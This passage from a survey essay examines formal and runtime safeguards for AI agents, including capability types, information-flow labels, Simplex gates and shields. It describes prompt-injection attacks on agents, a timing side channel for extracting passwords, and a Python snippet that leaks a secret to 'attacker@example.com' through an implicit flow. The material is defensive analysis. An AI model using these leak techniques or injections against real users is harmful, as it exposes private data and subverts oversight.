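*Trust but Verify* (2026) examines this with language models in both roles. In theory, if each round of questioning misses a false claim with probability at most *q*, all *T* rounds miss it with probability at most *q*ᵀ. With *q* = 0.5 and ten rounds, that is less than one in a thousand. But on Humanity's Last Exam, a set of very hard questions, the verifier's verdicts were hardly better than chance. More rounds help only if each gives the verifier a fresh chance to find the mistake. If the verifier lacks the knowledge to recognise the mistake,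 *q* is 1 and *q*ᵀ stays at 1 however many rounds there are.

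## Limiting what the model's code and data can reach

Agents act through tools, such as functions that read files, run commands or send email. These actions may do harm before the agent gives its final answer, so checking that answer isn't enough. Programming-language researcher Erik Meijer was preparing a talk about this danger when his coding agent wiped the contents of a source file.

AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026) records the talk, in which Meijer explains the danger with types. A model that only answers has the type

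Question → Answer

and a model with tools has the type

Question → IO Answer

where `IO` marks a computation that may act on the world while producing its result. Such a model can empty someone's bank account and then return a polite sentence, so a check on the sentence comes too late.

Meijer wants the model to return a program that describes the actions it would take. Ordinary code checks the program before anything runs. The idea comes from proof-carrying code, a technique from the 1990s in which the supplier of a program also provides a proof that it is safe, and the recipient only has to check the proof.

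A small example in Lean accompanies the talk. A plan can finish with an answer, read a file and continue, or delete a file and continue. Two rules define which plans are free of deletions:

- A plan that finishes immediately is free of deletions.
- A plan that starts by reading a file is free of deletions if the rest of it is, whatever the file contains.

A plan to read a source file and count its characters has a proof, but a plan that might delete something does not, because no rule covers deleting.

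The words "whatever the file contains" matter because of prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in data that an agent reads. Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* describes a user who asks an agent to summarise her inbox. One message contains instructions to send the summary to an outside address without mentioning it, and the agent follows them.

Meijer thinks nobody should let an agent act without a proof that its actions are safe. Tests can reveal harmful behaviour but can't rule it out, and people who have to approve every action soon click "Allow" without reading. These criticisms of the alternatives are fair, but a proof excludes only what somebody thought to define. In another of his examples, the task is to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the specification requires that neither file exists afterwards. A shorter program that deletes every text file in the folder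 also satisfies it, because it lacks the condition that all other files stay as they were. Meijer adds such a condition to the deletion tool, but the task needs one too, because a tool that deletes exactly the files matching `*.txt` still deletes too many.

### Capabilities

Rust guarantees memory safety for every safe program that compiles, so nobody has to write a proof for each one. A language can similarly restrict effects, such as opening a file or sending data, without a proof for each program if a program must hold a value called a capability to perform them. In most languages, any function can open a file by calling the standard library, but in a capability-safe language it needs a value that represents access to files, which it can't create itself. The cart's wrapper used the same idea when it kept the motor in a private field.

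Granting capabilities carefully doesn't stop every leak. An agent that summarises contracts may need to read them and communicate with a model in the cloud, so a sandbox would have to permit both. The agent leaks data when it puts text from the contracts into a message to the cloud, even though neither reading the contracts nor sending a message breaks a rule by itself.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* addresses this with Scala 3, a language whose experimental capture checking records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use. A function of type `String -> Int` takes text, returns a number and is pure, so it can't affect anything else. A function of type `String ->{notes} Unit` takes text, can use the capability `notes`, and returns nothing useful.

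The system, called TACIT, puts secret data in a container of type `Classified`. An agent's program can transform the contents only with a pure function, and the result goes into another such container. Here is a program that opens a folder and tries two things:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val report = readClassified("secret/incident.txt")
  val notes = access("notes.txt")

  report.map(text => text.length)          // accepted
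  report.map(text => notes.write(text))    // rejected
}
```

The first function measures the report's length and is pure. The second would copy the report into an ordinary file. The second function's type includes `notes`, but `map` requires a function that uses no capabilities, so the compiler rejects the program before any of it runs.

The compiler also rejects a program that could use the folder's capability after the block ends. For example, the block can't return a function that reads a file later, because that function's type would have to include a capability that doesn't exist outside the block. Rust's borrow checker prevents dangling references in much the same way.

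### From the model to the file system

TACIT works with ordinary agents, which don't need any information about its type system. The agent sends Scala code as a tool call. The compiler checks the code in a restricted safe mode, and the code runs only if it compiles. If it doesn't, the agent gets the error message and can try again.

Safe mode bans features that would let a capability go untracked, such as unchecked type conversions and reflection, which lets a program inspect and use parts of itself that are normally hidden. (Sound Rust code broke Sesame's privacy guarantee by reading private fields.) A program can reach files, other programs and the network only through one library. To use the network, for example, it must name the hosts it will contact, and the library checks them against an allowed list.

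The agent never sees secret text. When its program prints a `Classified` value, the user's terminal shows the contents, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. To summarize a secret report, the agent can send it to a second, trusted model running locally. The summary comes back in a `Classified` container too, so the agent can pass it on without reading it. This works only if the local model keeps nothing between requests.

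The design treats the agent's model as a possible attacker that may even cooperate fully with whoever wants the secrets. Its guarantee depends on the compiler, the library, the software that runs the compiled code, and the local model.

### How well TACIT worked

The experiments used a programming project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. Twelve ordinary tasks, each combined with ten prompt injections, gave 120 trials. Another eleven trials used direct requests for the secrets or pretexts, such as an administrator's emergency. Each trial ran once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once with them as plain text.

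| | With containers | Plain text |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, trials with a leak | 0 of 131 | 2 of 131 |
| MiniMax M2.5, trials with a leak | 0 of 131 | 11 of 131 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, ordinary tasks completed | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, ordinary tasks completed | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The type system predicts the zeros, so they mainly test whether the implementation works. The results in the plain-text column depend on how well each company trained its model to refuse. Sonnet's low completion rate there may be partly an artefact, because the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

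Writing typed programs seems to reduce agents' performance little, if at all, on some kinds of work. In six comparisons on simulated customer service, agents that wrote Scala did 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points better than agents that called tools in the usual way. On a set of real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without it.

The results on AgentDojo, a public set of tests for prompt injection, are more mixed. Only one of 1,926 attacks counted as a success. In that case, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews containing the name the attacker wanted it to mention. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* calls TACIT's usefulness comparable to that of CaMeL, an earlier defence, but the figures vary widely. TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks to CaMeL's 81% with one model, and 64% of the travel tasks to CaMeL's 1% with another.

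*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) takes a similar approach. The agent's programs must type-check together with the developer's code, so one policy covers both. An agent can also start further agents, which work under the same policy or a stricter one.

### Noninterference

`Classified` containers enforce a version of noninterference, the property that changing a secret doesn't change what an outsider sees. Noninterference also applies to trust. If two runs differ only in untrusted data, such as the text of a stranger's email, every protected action, such as a payment, must be the same in both.

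It is tempting to enforce this by labelling each value with its origin and blocking any secret value that is about to leave. That catches direct copying, but a program can also reveal a secret through what it doesn't do. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found such a leak in CaMeL, which runs an agent's program in an interpreter that labels values. The trick dates from the 1970s and looks roughly like this:

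```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the threshold. The first `if` depends on the secret balance, so CaMeL labels `tmp` as secret when it becomes false. The program then skips `rich = False`, so CaMeL never labels `rich` as secret. `rich` stays public and true, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. Either way, the attacker learns which side of the threshold the balance is on.

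CaMeL also retries a program that fails. Whether CaMeL's policy blocked the last attempt may depend on the secret, and the retry loop runs outside the part of the system that tracks labels. An attacker could therefore extract the whole secret, one bit per attempt.

### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda to rule out this class of mistake with a proof. Every value has a label, which may contain U for untrusted, S for secret, both or neither. A value computed from others gets every letter in their labels. If a program uses a secret to choose what to do, the result is secret too.

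The conversation with the model also has a label. Once a program puts a stranger's email into a conversation, everything the model writes there is untrusted, including any code, which runs with the same label. A function that sends money can then reject that output. To keep the main conversation free of untrusted text, a program can copy the conversation, clear the copy, ask about the email there, and then discard the copy, keeping only the labelled reply. Earlier defences, including CaMeL, built this separation into their architecture, whereas in LLMbda it is optional for each program.

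A program may not add to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret. If it tries, the run stops. This prevents the trick with `rich`, but an observer who notices that the program failed may still learn something.

The main theorem allows for that. An observer at level *m* sees only values whose labels are within *m*. Write *x* ~ₘ *y* if *x* and *y* look the same to that observer, and write ⟦*C*, *e*⟧ₘ for the probabilities of what the observer sees when program *e* runs after conversation *C*. These may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the probability that the run stops early or never finishes. In slightly simplified form, the theorem says that for every *m*,

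*C*₀ ~ₘ *C*₁ and *e*₀ ~ₘ *e*₁ ⇒ ⟦*C*₀, *e*₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦*C*₁, *e*₁⟧ₘ

The symbol ⌣ means that the two sets of probabilities are compatible:

*μ* ⌣ *ν* ⇔ there is an *ω* with *μ* ≤ *ω*, *ν* ≤ *ω* and total at most 1

If two starting points differ only in things the observer can't see, the observer could attribute any difference in the results to some runs not finishing.

Suppose a program prints yes or no. With one secret, it prints yes in 50% of runs, prints no in 30%, and never finishes in 20%. With another secret, the figures are 40%, 50% and 10%. The larger figure is 50% for yes and 50% for no. These add up to 100%, so the two sets of figures are compatible. A program that always finished, and printed yes 90% of the time with one secret and 10% with the other, would fail the test. Its larger figures would be 90% for yes and 90% for no, which add up to 180%, over the 100% limit.

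If a program always finishes, compatible probabilities must be equal, so the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the statistical distance between the two sets of results is at most the average probability of not finishing. In the first example, both this bound and the actual distance are 15%.

The proof constructs *ω* by running an altered version of the program. As soon as a computation involves something the observer can't see, the altered version skips it and returns a dummy value, so it behaves identically for both secrets. It also finishes at least as often as the original, because skipped computations can't get stuck. Its probabilities are therefore at least as large as the original's for both secrets, as compatibility requires.

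### The theorem's assumptions

The theorem holds for every LLMbda program and requires no assumptions about the model's training or intentions. The model can be any function that takes the current conversation and assigns probabilities to possible replies. The theorem also holds whatever the reply is and however the interpreter turns it into code.

That is broad, but narrower than "every behaviour" in the restated criterion, because the reply can depend only on the current conversation. If the hosting company gave the model memory of other conversations, a secret from a private one could appear in a public one, and the labels would not show the leak.

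Garby and colleagues checked the proofs in Lean and also wrote the interpreter in it. The interpreter is the harness, the ordinary code that calls the model and carries out its instructions. Another theorem shows that the interpreter's results have the probabilities given in the main theorem, provided the model's replies are random draws of the assumed kind. This is a considerable advantage over most work on agents, because proofs about a simplified description of a program can miss faults in the program itself. The proofs do not cover the code that contacts the model over the network.

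LLMbda's theorem doesn't cover real tools, because it assumes that all data sources are inside the program. In the tests, the bank account was a data structure. Anyone who connected a real bank would have to ensure that each piece of incoming data gets the right label and that every sensitive function checks the labels of its arguments.

### A weaker kind of type safety

Not every calculus with a safety theorem limits what an agent can do. Liu (2026), in *λ_A*, gives types to the parts of an agent, such as calls to a model, tools and loops. The main theorem, checked in Coq, says that an agent *e* of type *τ* either produces a value of type *τ* or fails a guard:

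⊢ *e* : *τ* ⇒ *e* returns a value of type *τ*, or a guard fails

A guard is a test that a developer attaches to an output, for example that it contains exactly three words. If the test fails, the agent is stuck, meaning that no rule defines its next step. An implementation can report an error or retry. Liu stresses that this is a defined error, not undefined behaviour, which makes it resemble a panic in Rust.

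The theorem applies to models that give the same reply each time and to tools that always return something. It would rule out passing a number to a tool that expects text. But a tool that deletes a file and a tool that counts the words in one can both take text and return text, so the types don't distinguish them. Liu leaves types that track effects to future work.

Liu also proves that a loop with a limit of *n* runs at most *n* rounds, which would cap its cost. Twenty rounds at one cent each could cost no more than 20 cents. However, the written proof assumes that each round restarts the loop at most once, and the typing rules don't enforce this. The loop body

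*λs*. *λx*. *s*(*s*(*x*))

has a valid type and restarts the loop twice. With a limit of 20, it can run 2²⁰ − 1 rounds, or about a million. The bound does hold for the usual agent loop, which restarts itself once per round.

### Exceptions and timing

A pure function can still fail, and its failure may reveal information. An agent could write a function that divides by zero if a secret password begins with A, or that puts the password in an error message. Banning such errors is impractical because almost any calculation can run out of memory. TACIT catches them and can put the failure in a `Classified` container like any other secret. This makes accidental mistakes harder to fix, because the agent's program appears to succeed, the user sees an empty result, and nobody gets an error message. The instructions for the AgentDojo tests warned models about this at some length.

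TACIT doesn't prevent an agent from learning secrets through timing. A pure function can finish at once if the password begins with A and otherwise count to a billion, so an agent that can measure the delay learns one bit. If the agent can repeat this with different yes-or-no tests, finding a 20-character password drawn from 64 possible characters takes 120 measurements. This attack requires a malicious agent, which TACIT's threat model explicitly includes. LLMbda's theorem doesn't cover timing either, because it describes only the results of a run, not its duration.

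### Code that everyone has to trust

Some useful library code breaks the rules of safe mode harmlessly. For example, a function may store its past results to avoid recomputing them. This changes data, which a pure function shouldn't do, but callers can't observe the change. Library authors can mark such code `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then accepts it without verifying that it is safe. The result resembles a Rust library that contains unsafe code, and a mistake in the marked code can undermine the guarantee for every agent that uses the library.

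*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* suggests that a proof like RustBelt's could show that this boundary is sound. Computer-checked proofs exist for the core of Scala's capture checking, but nobody has yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides its intended guarantees.

In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) proved more about the code between an agent and the world. They worked on PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents, using Dafny, a language whose compiler checks proofs. They represented the model as a function with no body, so the proof has to cover every action the function's type permits. They proved that every resulting effect obeys the policy.

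This covers rules about individual steps, such as which addresses an agent may write to. It doesn't establish noninterference, which requires comparing runs. Moon and Varshney also assume that every effect passes through the verified part, and they recommend adding a sandbox in case an effect bypasses that part.

An agent that may run commands can use them to get around these limits, because the compiler has no control over what a command does. TACIT's designers recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`. But `sbt`, which builds Scala projects, runs code from the project's own build files. An agent that can edit those files could use it to run code that safe mode would reject. Preventing this takes isolation by the operating system, much as Omniglot needed memory protection to confine C libraries.

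### Letting information through on purpose

Strict noninterference forbids many things that people want agents to do. If a user asks an agent to pay a bill, the amount and the account number come from the bill, which is untrusted. LLMbda therefore has an instruction, `endorse`, that relabels an untrusted value as trusted.

An agent might ask a model, in a separate conversation, to sort a stranger's email into one of eight categories. The agent could then endorse the category so that it can appear in the subject of a reply. The stranger can influence the choice of category, and so control at most three bits of the subject, but can't put arbitrary text there.

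A second theorem shows that using `endorse` never weakens the protection of secrets. But the protection against untrusted data no longer holds for whatever the program endorses. In the agent that Garby and colleagues built, the model writes the endorsements itself, so a badly behaved model could endorse everything. Protection against untrusted data therefore depends on the model again, unless the harness restricts where endorsements may appear.

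The agent, Randori, at least writes its plan before it sees any untrusted data. Agents usually need several attempts to write a working program, and an error message from a failed attempt might contain an attacker's text. Randori therefore tests and revises its program on artificial data until it works, then runs it on the real data.

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs. CaMeL completed 32 with its policy turned off and 18 with it turned on. Across three models, attackers succeeded in 2 of 1,296 attempts against Randori.

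That last figure overstates the labels' contribution. In about two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool that the agent had no reason to include in its plan, so writing the plan first was usually enough to stop it. The labels matter more in the remaining third, where attackers succeeded in 2 of 423 attempts. Writing the plan first isn't completely reliable either. When a task required following a file's instructions exactly, CaMeL wrote a program that could carry out whatever the file said. Two attacks succeeded this way with the policy off.

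### Permitted actions used badly

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described. The attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The agent read the file, endorsed the details and paid, as the user had asked. CaMeL's developers got a similar result on this kind of task and considered it outside what their defence was meant to prevent.

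Types and labels can show that the payment details came from a file, but not that the file is a real bill. The guarantee in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* likewise doesn't cover wrong results. An agent allowed to write to the summary file can fill it with nonsense, and an agent allowed to cancel bookings can cancel the wrong one.

Removing `endorse` blocks the payment attack but makes three of the sixteen banking tasks impossible. With one of the models, completed runs fell from 36 to 30. Garby and colleagues report a larger loss for Zhou and colleagues' system, which completed 15 of 21 tasks in a simulated workplace chat without its policies and 8 with them. Many of those tasks required sending information where no secure policy would allow it. Zhou's team suggests asking the user to confirm such cases, which brings back the problem that people approve requests without reading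 them.

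## Gates and fallbacks for models that act

Capabilities can block a model's access to a tool entirely, but a delivery cart is useless unless the model can drive it. Whether a command is safe then depends on the cart's position and speed.

Suppose the forbidden event is the cart hitting a wall. The cart travels at up to 2 metres per second, its brakes slow it by 1 metre per second each second, and the network issues a command every half-second. Refusing only the commands that would take the cart into the wall within that half-second is not enough to prevent a collision. If the cart is 1.2 metres from the wall, a command to continue at full speed passes this check, because the cart covers only 1 metre before the next command. It is then 20 centimetres from the wall and needs 2 metres to stop.

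The wrapper has to check whether the cart could still stop after carrying out the command. At full speed the cart needs 3 metres, 1 to carry out the command and 2 to brake. If the wall is 3.4 metres away, the wrapper admits the command and the distance falls to 2.4 metres. The wrapper then refuses the next command and brakes, and the cart stops 40 centimetres from the wall. The part of the wrapper that admits or refuses commands is a gate. Braking is the fallback, the trusted behaviour that takes over after a refusal.

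The same argument works for any machine with a suitable set *S* of recoverable states. The forbidden event must not happen in any state in *S*, and the fallback, started anywhere in *S*, must keep the machine in *S*. For the cart, *S* contains every state in which the distance to the wall is at least the stopping distance, which is *v*²/2 with these brakes. In state *x*, the gate admits action *a* only if

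*f*(*x*, *a*, *w*) ∈ *S* for every possible disturbance *w*

Here *f* predicts the next state, and *w* stands for anything the commands don't control, such as a slippery patch of floor. If the machine is in *S*, every admitted action keeps it there, and so does the fallback. By induction, a machine that starts in *S* never leaves it. *S* serves the same purpose as a vector's safety invariant, and the proof uses no facts about the network.

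### Simplex

Engineers call this arrangement the Simplex architecture. Sha introduces the idea in *Integrate Mixed-Criticality Components with Formalized Architectural Patterns* with two sorting programs, a fast, unverified one and a slow one proved correct. The wrapper lets the fast program rearrange the items but not change them, then checks in a single pass that they are in order. If the result is wrong or late, the slow program sorts the items instead. The output is correct whatever the fast program does, and would be even if a person replaced that program.

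A steering command is harder to check because there may be no way to tell whether it is the right one. Sha considers the command safe to carry out if the simple controller can handle the resulting state. The Boeing 777, for example, has a complex normal controller and a simpler secondary one that uses control laws from the 747, which had been in service for over 25 years. The normal controller should keep the aircraft within the range of conditions in which the secondary controller is stable.

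Nesti, Salamini and colleagues (2025), in *The Use of the Simplex Architecture to Enhance Safety*, built Simplex systems around neural networks on real hardware. In one, a network balances a rod upright by swinging the arm beneath it. Four numbers describe the state *x*, two angles and two speeds, and the recoverable set is an ellipsoid:

*x*ᵀ*Px* < 1

*P* is a matrix chosen to make the ellipsoid as large as possible. When the left side reaches 1, a simple controller takes over and keeps control until the value falls to 0.1, so that the two controllers don't alternate rapidly. When someone pushed the rod hard, it began to lose balance under the network's control, and the simple controller recovered it.

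This falls short of a proof because the monitor checks the current state, not the state that the next command would produce. Nesti and colleagues acknowledge that a guarantee requires predicting that next state. They left the prediction out because computing time was limited and the ellipsoid is much smaller than the true recoverable set. They sampled points on the edge of the ellipsoid, varied their model's parameters by 5%, and found no unrecoverable state, but they note that sampling can't provide an absolute guarantee.

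Their other system is a rover that drives along a corridor. As obstacles get closer, the wrapper limits the rover's speed to 1.5 metres per second, then to 1 metre per second, and then stops it. When someone threw a cardboard box in front of the rover, the wrapper triggered a stop within 100 milliseconds.

Nesti and colleagues set the distances in front of the rover by driving it at a wall at nearly its top speed of about 3 metres per second. They made the side distances smaller because the corridor is only about two metres wide and the rover would otherwise have kept stopping. They argued that the smaller distances were safe because the network's formula never produces a speed above 1 metre per second. This argument relies on a property of the model, so it no longer covers every behaviour. In a simulated attack that doubled the network's output, the wrapper limited the rover's speed in places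 and the rover still finished the course. This is encouraging, but a single run is weak evidence about other outputs.

### Keeping a safe plan in reserve

Simplex needs a fallback that somebody has verified in advance, which may be impractical for a machine as complicated as an aircraft. Mehmood, Sheikhi and colleagues (2021), in *The Black-Box Simplex Architecture for Runtime Assurance of Autonomous CPS*, replace that proof with a check at run time. At each step:

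1. The main controller proposes one command.
2. A second controller, which nobody has to trust either, extends the command into a complete plan.
3. A decision module simulates the plan. If the plan keeps the machine safe forever, the module stores it in place of the old one.
4. The machine carries out the first command of the stored plan.

For the cart, a plan might be to go forward for half a second, then brake and stand still. If either controller produces nonsense or takes too long, the module keeps following the old plan, which ends with the cart stopped. The stored plan is safe at the start, only another safe plan can replace it, and what remains of a safe plan after its first command is also safe. The machine therefore stays safe whatever the two controllers do, provided the module's predictions are accurate.

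A simulation can't run forever, so every plan must end in a state that is safe for some simple reason. Mehmood and colleagues require the aircraft to be flying nearly level, with the distance between each pair growing. If two aircraft then keep flying straight at constant speed, the square of the distance between them is a quadratic function of time that curves upwards, so once it starts to grow, it never shrinks.

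The test used simulated F-16 fighters and collision-avoidance networks intended for pairs of aircraft. With three aircraft and no decision module, two passed within 175 feet of each other. With the module and a limit of 1,500 feet, the smallest distance was 1,602 feet for three aircraft and 1,500.5 feet for 15.

A margin of half a foot shows how little the module has to interfere, but also how much depends on the model of the aircraft. The module made its predictions with the same model that the simulation used, so they were not subject to wind or sensor error. For a group of simpler robots, Mehmood and colleagues also had the module compute every position possible within a given amount of error, which took about two milliseconds.

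### Shields

Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues (2017), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding*, compute the gate, which they call a shield, before the model starts to act. In their example, a model learns to run a hot-water tank cheaply by opening and closing a valve. The tank holds 100 litres and must never overflow or run dry. Between 1 and 2 litres flow in each second while the valve is open, and up to 1 litre flows out whether it is open or not. To limit wear, the valve has to stay in each position for at least three seconds.

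The shield stops the model from opening the valve when the tank holds more than 93 litres. Three seconds can add 6 litres, so opening it at 94 could fill the tank. The shield also stops the model from closing the valve below 4 litres, because three seconds can drain 3 litres and empty the tank.

A program can find these limits by treating the problem as a game against the environment. It starts with the set of states that break no rule, then repeatedly removes any state in which every action might lead outside the set, until no such state remains. The remaining states form *S*, and the shield allows an action only if every possible result is in *S*. No separate fallback is necessary, because every state in *S* has at least one allowed action that the shield can substitute for a blocked one.

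Alshiekh and colleagues prove that the shield forbids an action only if some environment that fits the description of the tank could make that action lead to a violation. If a faulty pipe delivers 3 litres per second, the description is wrong and the guarantee no longer applies.

### Why retries defeat a gate

The tank's shield decides by exact calculation. Other gates apply a statistical test to each proposal, for example with a noisy sensor or a second network. *Generator-Independent Runtime Assurance under Partial Observation* (Wan, Xie and colleagues, 2026) examines when a gate's guarantee is independent of the model behind it, and shows that testing proposals one at a time isn't enough to ensure this.

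Suppose the cart reaches a junction where all ten aisles are blocked. A separate sensor covers each aisle, and the gate mistakes a blocked aisle for a clear one 5% of the time. If the model proposes one aisle and accepts the answer, the risk is 5%. But planning programs usually try something else after a refusal. If the sensors' errors are independent, the chance that the gate eventually admits a blocked aisle is

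1 − 0.95¹⁰ ≈ 0.40

With 50 blocked aisles it is 0.92. Repeated attempts are enough to cause this problem, even if the model isn't adversarial. They caused the same problem for the verifier that accepted 1% of wrong answers.

The effect depends on how the errors are related. Ten tries raise the risk from 5% to 50% if no two sensors ever fail together, but leave it at 5% if they always fail together.

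### Certifying a set of actions

Wan and colleagues' solution is for the gate to certify a whole set of actions at once. Let *V*(*x*) be the viable actions in state *x*, those that keep the machine safe and leave the fallback able to work. Before each decision, the gate computes a set *A* of certified actions. If the model's proposal is in *A*, the machine carries it out, and otherwise the fallback takes over. (As with any wrapper, the model must have no other route to the motors.)

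The gate has made an error if *A* contains even one action that isn't viable. According to the theorem, for any single decision,

max over all models of Pr[the machine carries out a non-viable proposal] = Pr[*A* ⊄ *V*(*x*)]

The machine only carries out proposals in *A*, so it can carry out a non-viable action only if *A* contains one. The left side therefore can't exceed the right. A model given both the true state and *A* can propose a non-viable action whenever *A* contains one, so the two sides are equal.

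In the junction example, the right side is 40%. A designer has to reduce this figure, because a guarantee about individual proposals doesn't cover the worst model. The theorem doesn't show that safety itself requires certifying a set, since a non-viable action only lacks a guarantee and may be harmless.

The gate can use the model's suggestions to make *A* smaller, but it mustn't use them to relax the check. If it waived the check whenever the model reported high confidence, a model that always reported high confidence could do anything.

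### The risk over a working day

The errors add up over time. If the gate's error probability at step *t* is at most α*ₜ*, then over *T* steps

Pr[the forbidden event ever happens] ≤ α₁ + … + α*_T* + η

where η is the probability that the safety case for the machine and its fallback is wrong. The bound still holds if somebody replaces the model halfway through, even with a hostile one.

A cart that makes two decisions a second will make 57,600 in an eight-hour shift. If each decision has a one-in-a-million chance of error and η is 0.001, the bound is 0.0576 + 0.001, or nearly 6% per shift, which few warehouses would accept.

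Wan and colleagues get a better bound by confining the uncertainty to the sensors. The gate keeps a set *C* of all the states that the measurements leave open, and certifies only actions that are viable in every one of them. If the distance to the wall is 3.4 metres, give or take 0.5, it could be as little as 2.9 metres. The cart needs 3 metres at full speed, so the gate refuses. The bound becomes

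Γ + ε₁ + … + ε*_T* + η

Γ is the probability that the true state is outside *C* at some point during the shift, and ε*ₜ* is the probability that the gate's calculation goes wrong at step *t*. If the calculation is exact, every ε*ₜ* is zero. With Γ and η both at 0.001, the risk for the whole shift is at most 0.2%.

Γ is easy to underestimate. If a state consists of 13 measurements, each with an independent 95% chance of being within its stated range, all 13 are within range only 51% of the time. The figure also has to hold for every model, so measuring the sensors' errors while a well-behaved network drives isn't enough, because another network might steer toward places where the sensors work badly.

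### Two situations that look alike

Better calculation can't replace missing information. Suppose the cart approaches a glass door, and its laser passes through the glass whether the door is open or closed. An open door exposes a reflector, which the laser detects in 30% of readings. The laser never detects the reflector when the door is closed.

Let α be the probability that the gate lets the cart drive on when the door is closed, and β the probability that it refuses when the door is open. Let δ be the largest difference between the two situations in the probability of any observation, which is 0.3 here. Wan and colleagues prove that

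α + β + δ ≥ 1

The gate's decision depends only on what it observes, so its chance of admitting the command can differ by at most δ between the two situations. It admits the command with probability α when the door is closed and 1 − β when the door is open, so 1 − β ≤ α + δ.

If the acceptable chance of hitting a closed door is 1%, the gate must refuse to go through an open one at least 69% of the time. Ten independent readings raise the chance of detecting the reflector at least once to about 97%, which lowers the minimum refusal rate to about 2%. But if the reflector falls off, δ is zero and the gate must refuse at least 99% of the time, however many readings it takes. The wrapper that had no way to detect whether a reader had already taken the maximum dose had the same problem.

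The cart can still work safely in such a building if its owners replace the glass door, or if the gate allows only actions that are safe in both situations, such as approaching the door but stopping short of it.

### Why "rarely" is harder to enforce than "never"

Wan and colleagues' gate tries to exclude the forbidden event completely, and the probabilities refer to the chance that it fails. A designer might prefer a rule that permits the event with some small probability. *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs* (Heck, Macák and colleagues, 2026) proves that a shield for such a rule can't always be both safe and as permissive as possible.

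Their proof uses essentially this small example. A robot is placed in one of two rooms with equal probability. Each room has a safe action and a disastrous one, and the rule permits disaster in at most half of all runs. A model that takes the disastrous action only in the left room obeys the rule, as does one that takes it only in the right room, but a model that takes it in both rooms causes disaster in every run.

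The shield has information only about the room the robot has entered. In each room, the third model behaves like one of the two obedient models, so the shield can't stop it without also interfering with a model that obeys the rule.

Many existing shields block an action if it raises the risk by more than a certain factor. Heck and colleagues show that these shields don't enforce any limit on overall risk, because several small risks can add up to a large one. When the rule is that something must never happen, a shield can be safe without ever interfering with a model that already obeys the rule.

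### How the assumptions compare with Rust's

Rust's criterion covers every client and every run. With an exact calculation, Wan and colleagues' guarantee has the form

∀*B*: Pr[*E*] ≤ Γ + η

It still covers every behaviour *B* of the model, but a probability replaces "no run".

It also needs a model of the machine and its surroundings. RustBelt's proofs depend on a model too, but Rust's developers decide what the language means, and they can fix the compiler if it does something else. Engineers can't make a warehouse floor match their model in the same way. If spilled oil halves the cart's braking, the stopping distance from full speed doubles to 4 metres, and a gate that allowed for only 2 will let the cart hit the wall. Engineers can include oil among the disturbances, but the cart will then need 5 clear metres to drive at full speed, even on a dry floor.

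A vector's `get` reads the exact `len` that the module last stored, but the cart's gate has only an estimate of the distance to the wall. *Science of Safe AI* (2025), the report of a workshop in Philadelphia, describes the lack of ground truth as a limit on runtime monitoring. *Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models* (Zheng, Ruchkin and colleagues, 2026) recommends a Simplex layer for machines that use large pretrained models. It warns that sensor noise and incomplete views carry over into the scene description that later checks depend on.

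Rust code always has a fallback. `get` can return `None`, and a program that can't continue safely can stop. A cart can usually stop too, but an aircraft in flight can't. In *Safety Guardrails in the Sky*, Singletary, Cohen and colleagues (2026) tested a gate on a modified F-16 fighter whose backup manoeuvre returns the jet to a normal condition such as level flight. As the jet nears the edge of the recoverable set, the system gradually blends this manoeuvre into the pilot's commands. In 14 scenarios over five flights, it kept the jet within its limits on altitude, position and acceleration, even when the pilot tried to exceed them. These flights are good evidence that the fallback works on a real aircraft, but they didn't test a learned controller.

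Programmers can also combine sound Rust libraries, provided the libraries make the same assumptions about safe code. Wan and colleagues' theorem covers only one gate, so two carts with a gate each would need a further argument, since the safety of both gates might depend on the same space staying empty.

### Gates around learned controllers

A layer that corrects a controller's commands can make it safe without making it useful. *Enforcing Ellipsoidal Constraints in Neural Networks with a Polynomial Safety Layer* (2026) compares a drone's controller with and without such a layer in simulated flights through narrow mazes. Before training, the drone hit a wall on every flight without the layer. With the layer, it never touched a wall, but it never reached its goal either.

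A gate also does nothing about events it wasn't defined to cover. *Mission-Level Runtime Assurance Framework for Autonomous Driving* (2026) reports that keeping a simulated car physically safe didn't keep its mission on track when it received faulty high-level commands. Failures counted in the tests included driving into a restricted zone. The tests also included a small trial with a pretrained network.

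A gate can even fail at its intended job. Zongo and Wei (2026), in *Runtime Safety Filtering for Learned Small UAS Separation Policies under GNSS Degradation*, simulated about 65 delivery drones at a time on crossing and merging routes. Every second, each drone sped up, slowed down or held its speed according to a network's output. They counted a near-collision when two drones came within 100 metres of each other. The simulation corrupted the drones' satellite-derived positions by up to 60 metres along each axis, in whatever way best concealed the danger.

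The gate worked out the most dangerous positions consistent with the readings and overrode any command that reduced the safety margin too quickly. It made almost no difference to the drones' safety. In its most cautious setting, it overrode nearly every command when the satellite errors were small, yet the drones were no safer.

Zongo and Wei then gave the worst-case positions to the network and let it choose for itself. Near-collisions fell from an average of 0.24 per simulation to 0.02. When the satellite signals were accurate, however, near-collisions rose from 0.02 to 0.08.

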